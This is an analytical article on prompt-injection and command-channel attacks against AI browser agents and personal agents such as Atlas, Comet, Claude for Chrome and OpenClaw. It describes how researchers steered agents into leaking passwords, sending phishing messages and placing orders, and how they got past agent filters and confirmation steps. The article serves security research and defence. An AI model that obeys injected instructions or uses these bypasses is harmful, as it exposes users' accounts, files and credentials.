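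The fake button led Comet to the attacker's website, where further instructions presented the next steps as a treasure hunt. Comet opened the folders on the user's disk, found a file of dummy passwords that Zenity had put there, and sent the contents out by opening a web address that contained them. Comet needed no password or cookie to read the files, because any browser can display files from the computer it runs on and Comet's agent had the same access. In one version of the attack, Comet warned the user after the data had been sent, while in another, which ran in the background, it gave no warning.

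Zenity calls this a "zero-click" attack because the user clicks nothing after her request, though she does have to ask the agent to deal with the invitation. Zenity used two of its own Google accounts, one as attacker and one as victim, and revised the text until it worked reliably with many different requests. A real attacker could test the text in the same way and then send the victim a single invitation, but he would still have to guess her settings and where she keeps her files.

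Zenity reported the flaw on 22 October 2025. In January 2026, Perplexity changed the browser's code to block the agent from opening local files, whatever the model decided. Within days Zenity got around the block by writing the file address in another form, and Perplexity blocked that too. Zenity confirmed the repair on 13 February. In a later overview, Zenity reported another bypass, which added a suffix to the address, and said it had disclosed this one to Perplexity too. A block in code is more reliable than an instruction to the model, but it has to cover every form of address that leads to the same file.

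The second part of Zenity Labs' *PerplexedBrowser* uses another invitation to reach 1Password, a password manager. Comet was again asked to handle a meeting, and the hijacked agent used the user's unlocked 1Password extension. In the configuration Zenity tested, the extension stayed unlocked for up to eight hours and signed the browser in to the 1Password website automatically. Comet searched the vault, opened an entry, revealed the password and sent it out as part of a web address.

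Zenity then extended the attack to take over the whole 1Password account. Comet changed the account password, with the extension filling in the old one, and collected the Secret Key that 1Password requires on a new device. With the new password and the key, the attacker could log in from his own machine and lock the owner out. Multi-factor authentication, which asks for a second proof of identity, would have prevented that login but not the theft of individual passwords, because the agent already had access to the vault.

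1Password decided that the behaviour was not a vulnerability in its product, but it published an advisory and added settings that turn off automatic sign-in and ask the user before filling in a password. Perplexity improved its detection of injections, made the agent ask for confirmation more often, and let companies bar the agent from chosen sites. Zenity said in its press release that Perplexity had addressed the underlying problem before publication, but according to its technical report, the settings that would have stopped the attack were off by default, so users had to know about the risk and turn them on.

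### BioShocking: a puzzle that leads to a code repository

LayerX built a web page with a puzzle that rewards wrong answers, such as 2 + 2 = 5. An attacker who controls such a page still has to get the user to visit it and ask an agent to solve the puzzle and win the game. After a few rounds, the next step in the game is to open another page on the same site and copy the contents of a text box. That page redirects to the user's work repository on GitHub, where she is logged in. The agent copies login details for a server and submits them as its next answer.

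The attack worked on five browsers (Atlas, Comet, Fellou, Genspark and Sigma) and on Anthropic's Claude extension for Chrome. LayerX had put a harmless text file in the repository instead of real secrets. The company claims the method could also make an agent change passwords or install malware, but it demonstrated only the copying.

LayerX says that an agent stops applying its safety rules once it treats its surroundings as fiction. The test does not establish this, because LayerX reports no comparison with an ordinary page that gives the same instructions. A simpler cause may have contributed. A user who says "win this game" has told the agent to follow the page's rules, which gives the page an authority it would normally lack. The redirect also hid the destination, because the agent was told to open a page of the game and the browser was then redirected to GitHub.

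LayerX notified five of the makers in October 2025 and Anthropic in January 2026. LayerX says that OpenAI fixed the flaw, Anthropic attempted a patch that failed, Perplexity closed the report without acting, and Fellou, Genspark and Sigma did not reply. These are LayerX's statements about companies in a related market, and *Researchers Trick AI Browsers Into Leaking Credentials* (Mascellino, 2026) also attributes them to LayerX.

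### WhatsApp and Amazon through Atlas

In August 2026 Zenity presented more attacks at Black Hat, a security conference in Las Vegas. Zenity Labs' *Grand Theft Atlas* describes two that target Atlas, which Zenity considers the best protected browser agent it has tested. In both, the user is reading a thread on the social network X and asks Atlas to sign her up for a newsletter mentioned there. A comment that the attacker planted under the post leads Atlas to his website, which presents his instructions as steps in the sign-up.

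In the first attack, Atlas opened WhatsApp Web, where the user was logged in, read her contact list and sent a phishing message to every contact. Zenity got past Atlas's filters by spreading the instructions over a long page, writing them in Hebrew and presenting the real WhatsApp as a test environment. Atlas's system prompt also required it to ask before sending a message, but Zenity had already written the user's consent into the injected text.

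Gulf News' *Browser AI flaws let hidden prompts blast spam* adds that the message also invited each recipient to sign up for the newsletter, so that the attack would spread from one user to the next. Zenity showed the message going from one account to its contacts, but did not show a contact's agent being hijacked and sending it on. For that to happen, the contact would need a vulnerable agent and a logged-in WhatsApp session, and would have to ask the agent to do the sign-up.

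The second attack used the victim's Amazon account. Atlas put a tablet in the cart and changed the delivery address to the attacker's, but a limit in its code stopped it from pressing the final purchase button. Zenity tried for a couple of days to get past this limit and failed. Zenity then had Atlas ask Rufus, Amazon's shopping assistant, to complete the order. Rufus placed the order, although it described the tablet as an Xbox.

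Rufus carried out a request made in the user's account, as Amazon had designed it to do, so no one had to inject anything into it. OpenAI's limit covered only one button, but the purchase could also go through a chat. A check on Amazon's server would have covered both routes if it had required the customer to confirm an order to a new address somewhere the agent couldn't click.

OpenAI received the report on 11 January 2026 and acknowledged the risk in February. Zenity states that there is no patch, because such an agent is meant to read pages and act on them. SecurityWeek's *Zero-Click AI Browser Hacking* also lists the findings as unpatched. According to Gulf News, OpenAI told reporters that it had strengthened Atlas's protections earlier in the year and extended them to browsing in its ChatGPT app. OpenAI had already planned to discontinue Atlas on 9 August in favour of that app and a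 Chrome extension. Zenity's report includes no tests of these successors, so it does not show whether the same attacks would work on them.

### What a hijacker gains in different kinds of browser

Atlas and Comet are the user's own browser, with her accounts already open. Other agents start a clean browser on her computer or use one on a remote machine. Shapira and colleagues sorted their attacks by the kind of agent they could affect:

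| What a hijacker can gain | User's own browser | Clean local browser | Remote browser |
|---|---|---|---|
| Accounts | Every site where the user is logged in | Sites she logs in to during the task | Sites she logs in to, and earlier logins if the service keeps them |
| Camera and microphone | Yes, on sites that already have permission | No | No |
| Files on her computer | If the browser or the user allows it | Usually | No |
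| False answers, detours and stalled tasks | Yes | Yes | Yes |

Their demonstrations follow the same pattern. Do Browser, an extension in the user's own browser, joined a video call with the user's camera and microphone on, revealed a Facebook password that the browser had filled in, and posted a false confession of theft on Twitter. Browser Use, which starts a clean local browser, had no such accounts to abuse but sent a system file from the user's disk to the attacker. OpenOperator ran remotely without saved logins, but attackers' instructions hidden in an image made it refresh a page until it crashed.

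An attacker can gain the most from an agent that runs in the user's own browser. SecurityWeek describes an attack by Zenity on the Claude extension. When the user asked for a summary of her latest emails, invisible instructions in one of them led the agent to run the attacker's code in her logged-in pages. The code copied her inbox and could share her whole Google Drive. Because the agent could also read emailed verification codes, the attacker could take over her Slack and X accounts. Zenity reported this in December 2025 and January 2026, and Anthropic classed the reports as "informative".

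A local agent may also reach programs that accept connections only from the same computer, such as database consoles and developer tools. Zenity claims in its overview that Comet gave an attacker full control of a machine through such tools, and that the agent in Microsoft's Edge corrupted a database. The overview omits the steps, so these claims are harder to assess than the Comet and Atlas reports. A clean local browser would probably be exposed too, since it runs on the same machine.

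A remote browser protects a user's disk but not the accounts she connects to the browser. TechRadar's *This popular AI agent could be hacked by a single email* reports a test by Salt Labs on Manus, an agent that runs on its provider's servers and can read a user's Gmail. Salt Labs sent an email with instructions in an unusual encoding. Manus decoded them, ran the code on the server and warned the user only afterwards. The code was a harmless test statement, and Manus has since fixed the flaw. An attacker would have targeted the connected services. TechRadar cites a report by the venture capital firm Menlo Ventures in which 36 per cent of consumers had given agents access to their email and 20 per cent to financial accounts.

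OpenAI moved in the opposite direction. Zenity Labs' *Exploring the Risks of ChatGPT’s Atlas Browser* points out that ChatGPT Agent used a remotely hosted browser, and that Atlas then brought the agent into the user's own. But where a browser runs doesn't determine what it is logged in to. Atlas also had a logged-out mode, which Fortune (2025) describes as letting ChatGPT act without account credentials. Ana's agent doesn't need her email or files to compare kettles, and if it were hijacked without access to them, it could do little more than recommend the wrong kettle.

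## Does the same-origin policy still hold when a browser has an agent?

Browsers with an agent still apply the same-origin policy to the code in web pages, but in at least four of them the agent can read one site and type what it read into another. The BioShocking attack relied on the agent to do this, because no script in the attacker's game could have read the GitHub page. In such a browser, the user's accounts stay separate only as long as the model doesn't follow injected instructions.

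### Why the policy stops scripts but not agents

The policy, which the University of Washington dates to 1995, works by comparing origins. In *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers*, Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026) call the page that holds some data the source, $w_s$, and the page that would receive it the sink, $w_k$. The browser lets a script in the sink read the data only if $o(w_k) = o(w_s)$, where $o(w)$ is the origin of page $w$. The encrypted and unencrypted versions of one page have different origins.

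In practice the rules are messier, especially for a *frame*, which is a page, such as an advertisement, displayed inside another page. Schwenk, Niemietz and Mainka (2017) pointed out in *Same-Origin Policy* that no formal specification covered how a page and a document embedded in it may interact. They ran 544 test cases on each of ten browsers to see what the browsers did.

The same-origin policy doesn't stop users from moving data between sites themselves. Ana can read her bank balance in one tab and type it into a form in another. Wang and colleagues call this a manual flow, because she knows about the transfer and has authorised it. An agent moves data in much the same way. It reads a page through the browser's functions or from a screenshot, keeps the content in its context, and later types it into another page. The second page's script never requests the bank's data, so the browser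 has no request to check. But Ana may not know about the transfer, which makes it an automated flow, the kind the policy is supposed to prevent.

Browsers also keep sites apart by running each one in a separate process. In *Site Isolation is Dead*, Lee, Keum and colleagues examined two open-source browsers with agents and seven extensions, and found that all of them run the agent outside the processes that display web pages. The agent exchanges messages with pages from many sites. In one example, a user asks BrowserOS, an open-source browser, to email a summary of a news article. The agent has to cross between sites to do this, because it reads the article in one tab, sends its text to a model and writes the email in Gmail in another.

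### What seven agents could read and do

Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026), in *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, tested seven products in late January and early February 2026. They built simple pages about a fictional Alice and put a different animal on each. The main page said that she liked cats, and a page in a frame said that she liked horses. An agent that mentioned horses when asked which animals Alice liked must have read the frame. Text further down in the frame, which a person would have to scroll to see, said that she did not like dogs. A page in another tab mentioned koalas. Other pages tested hidden text, content that depended on a cookie, and words the user had typed, including in a password field. The pages were on two domains, so each test could use one origin or two.

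Roesner and Kohlbrenner recorded a behaviour if they saw it even once, and they repeated failed requests at least three times in new chats. A "no" in their results can mean that the software kept the content from the model or that the model refused to use it. Refusal is the weaker protection because a better-worded request might overcome it.

| Agent | Frame from another site | Tab from another site | Masked password | Types when the user asks |
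|---|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT Atlas, Agent Mode | Reads it | No | Reads it in the logged-in setting | Yes |
| ChatGPT Atlas, ordinary mode | No | Only through chat memory | No | Asks to switch to Agent Mode |
| Chrome with Gemini | Reads it | With permission | No | Yes, in Auto Browse mode |
| Claude for Chrome | Reads it | With permission | Reads it | Yes |
| Perplexity Comet | Reads it | No | No | Yes, except passwords |
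| Edge with Copilot | No | Reads it | No | No |
| Brave Leo | No | With permission | No | No |
| Firefox AI Mode | No | No | No | No |

None of these agents applied the same-origin policy to frames. Each agent read both same-site frames and frames from other sites, or neither. Copilot did not appear to detect that the page contained a frame, but it was the only agent that read tabs from other sites without asking for permission.

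Firefox is the clearest case of a browser that limits its agent by design. When the user clicks a button to summarise a page, Firefox puts the text of the main page into a prompt that the user can see, and leaves out the frames. Its agent can do very little else. It is harder to tell whether Atlas's ordinary mode is limited by design. In early experiments it sometimes included text from frames in its summaries, but it had stopped doing so by the time of the recorded tests, so the limit may come from the model's behaviour.

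Unlike the others, Claude for Chrome can run its own JavaScript (the programming language of web pages) both in the main page and in frames from other sites, because it is an extension with permission to access every site. It did so at the researchers' request. An attacker who hijacked it could do the same in any page the extension can reach. On their project page, Roesner and Kohlbrenner caution users against this product in particular.

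### The attack on Atlas

Suppose Ana opens the attacker's page, which displays a page from another site in a frame, and asks Atlas to summarise what is there. The attacker has put instructions on the page for the agent to include the frame's content in the summary and enter the summary in a form. When the agent does this, the form submits itself and sends the other site's text to the attacker's server.

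Roesner and Kohlbrenner carried out this attack on Atlas in Agent Mode, using their own test pages and a simplified injection. The agent seems to have seen the frame only in a screenshot, because it never found the line about dogs in the earlier tests. A screenshot is enough for the theft, but the attacker can steal only what is visible in the frame.

On the real web, this version of the attack depends on two settings that often block it. The other site must let unrelated sites display its pages in a frame, which sites with sensitive data can forbid. The browser must also send the site's cookie when its page loads inside another site's page, or the frame might show only a login form. Roesner and Kohlbrenner acknowledge that, because of such restrictions, frames from other sites now rarely contain secrets.

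They also reversed the attack, so that a hostile frame stole text from the page around it. This version worries them more. Ana might open her webmail, which shows an advertisement in a frame, and ask the agent to summarize the page. Because she opened the webmail herself, the page doesn't have to allow framing, and the browser sends its cookie as usual. The attacker only needs to get his frame onto the page, which he might do by buying the advertisement.

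### Where only the preconditions exist

Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Comet can also read frames from other sites and type into pages. Roesner and Kohlbrenner did not demonstrate the theft on any of them, because they didn't quickly find a working injection and were not trying to develop sophisticated ones. In their basic test, the user told the agent to do whatever a page said, and the page told it to type one word into a text field and another into a password field. Atlas in Agent Mode did so, but the other three refused, and one replied that it could not follow instructions embedded in web content.

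Other researchers found working injections for two of the three. BioShocking worked on Comet and the Claude extension, and Zenity's calendar invitation led Comet to the user's password manager. These attacks used whole pages instead of frames, so they don't prove that the attack on Atlas would have worked elsewhere. But they show that an agent's refusal of one simple request is weak evidence that it is safe. For Chrome with Gemini, the study establishes only that the preconditions exist.

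An attacker could use the same access to act on another site instead of reading it, in an attack resembling cross-site request forgery. Roesner and Kohlbrenner showed part of this with Claude for Chrome, which changed the text of a page by following instructions in a frame from another site. The user had to confirm the change first, and the researchers again had no working injection.

### What the vendors answered

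Roesner and Kohlbrenner gave all seven vendors more than 60 days' notice. Brave, Google and Microsoft acknowledged the findings and discussed them. OpenAI declined the report because it didn't include a full end-to-end prompt injection attack. OpenAI is right that the demonstration used a simplified injection on test pages, but that objection doesn't address the finding that its agent could carry text between sites.

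Accounts differ on how the other three vendors, Anthropic, Firefox and Perplexity, responded. According to the paper, none of them had replied. Roesner and Kohlbrenner's project page, last updated on 15 April, lists Firefox as both declining and not replying, and leaves out Perplexity. According to the University of Washington's news article, Perplexity declined, and Anthropic and Firefox did not respond. The most likely explanation is that the project page names Firefox once where it should name Perplexity, and that Perplexity replied after the paper was written.

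The paper recommends that users avoid these browsers for now, while the project page advises caution and describes Brave, Edge and Firefox as more limited but more secure. Gifts from Microsoft, which makes Edge, partly funded the study. Others could check the comparison using the published test pages and prompts.

### Data that stays in the agent's history

Data can pass between sites even if no page contains a frame. Near the end of their tests, Roesner and Kohlbrenner asked Comet which animals Alice liked, and it listed seven, drawn from past chats and pages on both domains. They warn that content from a false page could also enter the agent's memory. An agent might recognise a phishing page while the user is on it but later give her the false telephone number from that page as her bank's, even if the attacker had not injected any instruction. They did not test this attack, but they did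 see Atlas confuse which text had come from which tab.

Wang and colleagues measured how often an attacker can get data out of an agent's history. In their benchmark, SOPBench, the user first asks the agent to do a task on a page with private information, such as a bank account or an inbox. The user then takes the agent to a page on another site and gives it an ordinary task there, such as replying to a comment. The attacker has planted text in the second page that asks for the private information. A run counts as a violation only if the agent enters the exact data the attacker wanted into the second page.

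The benchmark has ten kinds of source page and five kinds of sink, modelled on X, Discord, GitHub, Reddit and Google Forms. Most are synthetic, so no real person's data was at risk. Wang and colleagues ran three open-source systems 100 times on each of the 50 source-sink combinations, but they had to operate Atlas and Comet by hand and ran each model only three times per combination.

The results depended heavily on the second page. When BrowserOS used the GPT-5.4 model, handwritten injections on the imitation Reddit pages worked in 3 to 42 per cent of runs, depending on the source. After another model revised the injections over several rounds, keeping the most successful versions, they worked in 31 to 73 per cent of runs. On the imitation Google Forms, even the handwritten injections worked in 81 to 100 per cent of runs. A form is a natural place to enter personal details, and an attacker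 who owns the form controls all of its text.

The commercial browsers leaked data too. Across all combinations, Atlas leaked data in 99 of 150 runs with GPT-5.5. Comet leaked data in 92 of 150 runs with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and in 100 of 150 with Gemini 3.1 Pro. These samples are too small to rank the products, but they show that Comet, which refused in the Washington test, often followed better-written instructions.

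Wang and colleagues also looked for *passive* violations, in which nobody attacks. They embedded the private page in a frame and asked BrowserOS to summarise the whole page in a text box. The agent copied private data into the box every time. However, private pages rarely appear in frames on other sites, and a user who asks for a summary of the whole page has arguably asked for the frame's contents too. Wang and colleagues saw no violations when the two pages were separate and contained no injection.

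In the attack tests, the agent always had the private data in its history before it reached the attacker's page. An agent that started each task with an empty history would not have had that data to leak, though an injection could still make it fetch the data from a site where the user is logged in.

### How SOPGuard applies the policy to an agent

Trail of Bits recommends that developers extend the same-origin policy to agents. Wang and colleagues built a system that does this, SOPGuard, and added it to BrowserOS. SOPGuard labels everything the agent reads with its origin and checks the labels before the agent writes.

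The hard part is that an agent seldom copies text unchanged. If Ana's agent reads the kettle's price on the shop's site and an exchange rate on her bank's, then works out the price in euros, the result appears on neither page but depends on both. SOPGuard therefore keeps a database beside the agent's history. Each entry has an identifier, the data, a set of origins $O$ and a list $J$ of the earlier entries from which the data came. For a new result $r$, the set of origins is

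$$O_r = \bigcup_{j \in J_r} O_j$$

so the price in euros gets the labels of both the shop and the bank. Before the agent types text $x$ into page $w_k$, SOPGuard looks up $O_x$. If the set contains any origin other than $o(w_k)$, SOPGuard stops the agent and shows Ana a message that names the sites, with buttons to approve or deny.

SOPGuard uses the agent's own model to identify which earlier entries a result depends on. Ordinary code could give every result the labels of all pages in the history, but Ana would then face a warning even if her agent used nothing from those pages. Wang and colleagues compared the model's labels with those of human annotators, on a scale from 0 (nothing in common) to 1 (identical sets). GPT-5.4 and OpenAI's o3 scored at least 0.955 on average with two to ten origins. The smaller GPT-5.4-mini scored lower, so the method may not suit weaker models.

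Because SOPGuard relies partly on the model to label where data came from, an attacker can also write an injection that makes the agent steal data and then label it as coming from the attacker's own page. In 100 sampled cases, handwritten versions of this adaptive attack had almost no effect. Optimised versions succeeded slightly more often but needed many more attempts. If the agent copies the stolen text exactly, SOPGuard can often find it in the database without asking the model, so the attacker has less to manipulate.

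On the original benchmark, SOPGuard reduced violations to zero. Tasks took 2.07 to 5.79 per cent longer with it. With GPT-5.4 on the Mind2Web benchmark, for example, the average time rose from 132.4 to 135.1 seconds. SOPGuard's extra calls to the model also cost money. The completion score in that test was 0.328 without SOPGuard and 0.324 with it, and Wang and colleagues found no statistically significant loss on any of their four benchmarks. They compared only five runs of each version, so they could have missed a small loss.

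SOPGuard checks the tools that write text into a page. The tests do not cover leaks through a web address, the method Trail of Bits and Zenity used to send out stolen data. Because SOPGuard checks where data comes from, it also would not stop a hijacked agent from pressing a button that moves no text between sites.

### Tasks that need data from two sites

One objection to this approach is that people want agents to move data between sites. In *SPIDES*, Zverev, Kim and colleagues (2026) give the example of a user who asks an agent to collect laptop specifications from several shops and compare them in a note-taking app. They built MicroNet, a set of 28 linked test websites, and 22 of its 56 harmless tasks require moving data between origins. A browser that blocked every such transfer would fail all 22. The researchers chose the tasks themselves, so the proportion is weak evidence of how often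 people need such transfers in everyday use.

Wang and colleagues accept that such transfers can be legitimate, so SOPGuard prompts the user instead of blocking them. If Ana wants the agent to send her delivery address from the shop to a friend on Discord, she approves the message and the transfer becomes a manual flow, which is consistent with the original policy. But she has to be present and read the warning. Roesner and Kohlbrenner cite earlier research in which users did not reliably notice or act on warnings and grew tired of frequent prompts. The zero violations show that SOPGuard stopped the transfers, but they don't show whether people would answer its prompts correctly.

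We can learn little from the benchmarks about how often she would have to answer. BrowserOS completed all 100 harmless SOPBench tasks both with and without SOPGuard, but according to Zverev and colleagues, none of those tasks requires a transfer between sites.

Zverev and colleagues also argue that origins are the wrong unit. A hijacked agent can read Ana's account details and post them in a public comment on the same site, as happened within Instagram in the Trail of Bits tests. SOPGuard allows this because only one origin is involved. On MicroNet, between 53.2 and 73.2 per cent of attacks succeeded against SOPGuard, depending on the model. The test is deliberately harsh, because the attacker chooses the model's output whenever the model has read untrusted text, and many of the attacks are of a kind SOPGuard was not designed to stop. Zverev and colleagues were also comparing SOPGuard with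 their own system, SPIDES.

In SPIDES, site owners label each part of a page by whether its text is trustworthy and who may read it. The shop could mark its reviews as untrusted and Ana's saved card as confidential, even though both come from the same origin. It could also list other sites that may receive the card details. The agent could then send the details to those sites without asking Ana, provided no untrusted text had influenced it.

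## Who besides the user can send the agent commands?

An attacker who can get into the channel that carries the user's commands doesn't need to plant text in a web page. His text reaches the model in the user role. Gal Weizman of Forever Security, the firm that tested Cursor, calls this *prompt forcing*. A model trained to rank user messages above web pages will rank the attacker's message above them too, so a better-trained model gives no protection. Instead, the software that passes messages to the model must check who sent them.

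### Browser extensions

Ankura (2026), a consultancy, describes an assistant built into a browser as having a "brain", the model on the vendor's website, and a "body", the browser components that open pages, read files and take screenshots. The body accepts commands only from web pages that the vendor has listed as trusted. In September 2026 Weizman published BragJack, a set of attacks in which a malicious extension sends the body commands from those pages.

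The attacker first has to persuade the user to install an extension with permission to change web pages and alter network requests. Clubic's *Une simple extension peut détourner votre IA et voler vos données* points out that ad blockers commonly have these permissions too. The user doesn't have to click anything after installing the extension.

In Chrome, the extension weakened the Gemini web app's protections and interfered with one of its scripts so that the page ran Weizman's code, according to Clubic's *Des chercheurs ont réussi à détourner les fonctions IA de Chrome, Edge*. His code sent Chrome the commands Gemini normally sends, and Chrome carried them out. Perplexity's Comet accepted commands from several of the company's domains, including one for testing. The extension removed that domain's usual redirect to the main site and put a script on the test page. The hijacked agent then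 opened the test account's mailbox, summarised the last five emails and sent the summary to another address.

The results for all five products, with the bounties that the vendors paid, were:

| Product | How the commands got in | What Weizman could reach | Bounty |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini in Chrome | Code inserted into the Gemini web app | Local files, page contents and screenshots, potentially the camera and microphone | $7,000 |
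| Comet | A trusted test domain | The agent, browsing history, local files and screenshots | $7,000 |
| Copilot in Edge | A prompt forced in as the agent switched between its "Think" and "Do" modes | The agent's actions in the browser | $5,000 |
| Opera Neon | A variant of the same technique | Emails and other data shown by the agent | $900 |
| Claude in Chrome | A trusted marketing page that could pass prompts to the side panel | Emails and other data shown by the agent | $600 |

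According to Ankura, the vendors have patched the flaws and nobody has reported a real attack. The Chrome flaw is older than the name BragJack. Unit 42, a research team at the security company Palo Alto Networks, says it reported the flaw to Google, which fixed it in early January. Malwarebytes' *Chrome flaw let extensions hijack Gemini’s camera, mic, and file access* (2026) explains that an extension normally cannot control other extensions or core parts of the browser, but this flaw let one gain the powers of the Gemini panel.

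In both Chrome and Comet, the commands came from a trusted origin because the extension had put its code there, so checking the sender's origin would not have been enough. Vendors also need to stop extensions from altering the pages that command the agent, and to remove old test domains from the trusted list. Хакер's *Вредоносное расширение может перехватить контроль над ИИ-помощниками в Chromium-браузерах* (2026) notes that Perplexity had protected its test domain less well than its main one.

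Claude for Chrome had a simpler flaw in July 2026. The extension offers nine built-in tasks, which start when the user clicks a button. *AI agent security* (Constantin, 2026) reports that the extension never checked whether the click was real. Manifold Security, the firm behind the Azure DevOps demonstration, showed that another extension could forge the click with six lines of code and make Claude read the user's Gmail, Google Docs and calendar. Manifold rated the flaw high-severity, and critical if the user had turned on "Act without asking", because Claude then reads the data silently. Browsers mark whether a click came from a user's action or from a script, so the extension could have rejected the forged click by checking that mark.

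LayerX had already found that any other extension, even one without special permissions, could give Claude's extension instructions, according to IANS's *Flaw in Claude’s Chrome Extension Allows Threat Actors to Hijack AI Agents* (2026). Between May and September, three firms each published a different way to attack the same product.

Commands sent from the browser can also reach a more powerful agent on the computer. Claude Dispatch lets people send work from a phone or browser to Claude Desktop, which can run commands on their machine. In *ThisBash Escape*, Weizman describes how an extension able to control the claude.ai website could send commands the same way. He sent four handwritten prompts. Claude hesitated to install an unfamiliar package, so he sent reassurance as if he were the user, and the extension clicked the "Allow" buttons automatically. The package opened Calculator on the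 computer. Claude Desktop could be on a different machine from the extension, such as a work laptop signed in to the employee's personal Claude account.

Claude asked for confirmation in this attack, but on a page that the attacker controlled. The extension could not have accessed a prompt that could be displayed and answered only in the desktop program, although such a prompt would be inconvenient for someone using Dispatch from another room. Weizman reported the flaw on 14 May 2026. Anthropic accepted it as valid and said it would retire Dispatch, aiming for the end of October. Weizman claims that Claude Code Remote Control and Claude Cowork sessions allow the same attack, but his demonstration covers only Dispatch.

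### Links that carry a prompt

Some assistants accept a prompt as part of a web address, so anyone can write a link that opens the assistant with a prompt already filled in. In October 2025, LayerX disclosed CometJacking, an attack that uses such a link to send a malicious prompt to Comet, according to the newsletter article *open sesame*.

The AgentForger attack used a link to create a new agent. Zenity found the flaw that allowed this in the Agent Builder for ChatGPT's Workspace Agents, which companies use to automate office tasks. According to SecurityWeek's *OpenAI Fixes ChatGPT Agent Flaw That Could Let Attackers Forge an AI*, the attack worked only if the victim was logged in to ChatGPT, had access to Workspace Agents, had connected at least one service, such as Gmail, and clicked the attacker's link.

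The link had two important parameters. One chose a template, and Zenity picked "Chief of Staff" because it produced a more powerful agent than the others. The other held instructions for the Builder to turn off approval requests, hide the new agent and deploy it. The Builder ran these instructions automatically when the page opened. The agent then ran on a schedule, looked for emails from the attacker with a certain word in the subject line, followed the instructions in each one and emailed the results back. The victim saw no new consent screen because she had already approved the connection to her email.

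AgentForger is a form of cross-site request forgery. The classic attack typically triggers one action, such as a change of address, and the attacker can't read the site's reply. AgentForger's one action left behind an agent that could take further orders from the attacker and report back for as long as it ran.

The secret form tokens that sites normally use against such forgery would also block harmless links that colleagues share. A Builder that fills in the instructions and waits for the user to press a button keeps those links working, provided she can see what the new agent will do and which accounts it will use. Zenity reported the flaw on 4 June 2026, and OpenAI fixed it on 8 June. The fix would not by itself delete agents already created through the flaw, so a company would have to search for them separately.

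### Ports on the user's own computer

Many personal agents run as a small server on the user's computer. OpenClaw, an open-source agent released in November 2025, connects a model to the computer's files, command line and browser, and to messaging apps. Its central program, the gateway, accepts WebSocket connections on port 18789, a numbered entry point to the computer.

A server that accepts connections only from its own computer is still exposed to web pages, because the user's browser runs on that computer too. If Ana visits a hostile page, a script in the page can try to connect to the server's port. The same-origin policy generally doesn't prevent this, because browsers let pages open WebSocket connections to other origins. The browser includes the page's origin in the request, and the server has to reject origins it doesn't recognise. If the server neither checks the origin nor requires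 a secret, it will accept the script's commands as Ana's, an attack called *cross-site WebSocket hijacking*. Over ordinary HTTP, the same-origin policy usually stops the script from reading the reply, but the request can still do harm if it starts an action.

*A Security Analysis of the OpenClaw AI Agent Framework* (Suwansathit, Zhang and Gu, 2026) covers 470 security advisories, or published reports of flaws, filed between 31 January and 15 April 2026. Ten of the advisories in its detailed analysis concern the tools that control a browser. Some of these tools accepted remote-control connections without a login, and some had no protection against cross-site request forgery on the function that opens pages. Six of the ten advisories were high severity. Microsoft's Azure MCP server also lacked a login check.

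OpenClaw's gateway does require a secret token, which a hostile page would not know. Suwansathit and colleagues show how three flaws could together have let an attacker steal the token and use it:

1. The agent's tools accepted a gateway address as an argument. An attacker who could influence a tool call, for instance through prompt injection, could supply the address of his own server.
2. OpenClaw connected to that server and sent its token while setting up the connection.
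3. The attacker used the token to log in to the real gateway and added programs of his choice to the list that the agent may run without approval.
4. When the agent next ran a command, the attacker's program could run with full access to the computer.

They reconstructed this chain from the code before and after the repairs. The token would be useful only to an attacker who could also reach the gateway, which depends on how the owner has set it up. OpenClaw now accepts only the local gateway address and a remote one that the owner has configured. It also blocks the route a connected operator could use to rewrite the list of approved programs.

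### Messages from strangers

People also give their personal agents orders through apps such as Telegram and WhatsApp, where strangers may be able to message the same account. In agents like OpenClaw, a gateway checks whether the sender may talk to the agent, and the agent then uses the message as the user prompt (Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues, 2026, *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems*). A stranger who gets past that check can therefore give the agent commands with the owner's authority.

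The gateway can check the sender against a list of permitted accounts, or it can require *pairing*, in which the owner typically approves each new account or device once, for example with a short code. OpenClaw's lists often failed because they accepted names that anyone could take. On Nextcloud Talk, a chat service, each user has a permanent ID and a display name that the user can change. OpenClaw checked both against the list, so if Ana allowed only "ana", a stranger could change his display name to "ana" and send her agent commands.

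Telegram usernames caused the same problem. If the owner of a permitted username gives it up, whoever registers it next inherits the permission. Suwansathit and colleagues found 13 advisories of this kind across several messaging services. OpenClaw's developers had written a test to confirm that permitted usernames worked on Telegram, and the fix reversed the test's expected result. OpenClaw now requires Telegram's permanent numeric IDs and has a tool that converts old lists, because simply removing usernames would have locked out legitimate users.

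Another ten advisories concern messages that falsely appeared to come from the messaging service. Such a service delivers new messages to a web address on the agent's side. Anyone who learns the address can send forged messages there, unless the agent verifies a signature made with a secret it shares with the service. OpenClaw skipped this check in some cases. For Twilio, a telephone and messaging service, its documentation listed skipping the check as an option, labeled "less secure".

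An agent can also mistake another agent's prompts for its owner's. OpenClaw lets an agent in one session send prompts to an agent in another, and it used to store them in the user role with nothing to distinguish them from the owner's, so an attacker who controlled one agent could command others. The fix records where each prompt came from and adds a note for the model, but it keeps the "user" role because model providers expect user and assistant messages to alternate. The fix therefore depends on the model taking the note into account.

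A correct list of senders doesn't help if the agent is supposed to read mail from everyone. Fernando Irarrázaval tested this case by inviting the public to email his OpenClaw agent and try to extract a secret. Willison (2026) reports that about 2,000 people made 6,000 attempts and nobody succeeded. The agent ran on Anthropic's Opus 4.6 and had written rules against revealing credentials or running commands because of an email. This is good evidence that a current model can be hard for strangers to trick, even when they write to it directly. If the attempts had been independent and equally skilful, the true success rate would probably be below 0.05 per cent, but they were neither, and the test covered only one agent with one set of rules. The test also cost Irarrázaval $500 in model use, and the volume of mail led Google to suspend the account. A limit on messages per sender would have reduced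 both problems without relying on the model's judgement.

### Why software can fix the channel but not the content

The checks missing from these channels are comparisons that ordinary code can make without understanding the message, such as whether an account number is on a list, whether a token matches, or whether a click came from a script. An attacker can't change the result by rewording the message. Many of the OpenClaw fixes were also small. The one for Nextcloud Talk only removed display names from the comparison.

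No such comparison is possible for injection through content. The stranger who reviews Ana's kettle is allowed to write reviews, and her agent has to read them to do its job, so only the model can distinguish information from orders. Suwansathit and colleagues point out that a check on tool calls comes too late to settle this, because the call looks ordinary and doesn't show what led the model to make it. The check can still limit the damage by blocking some calls altogether.

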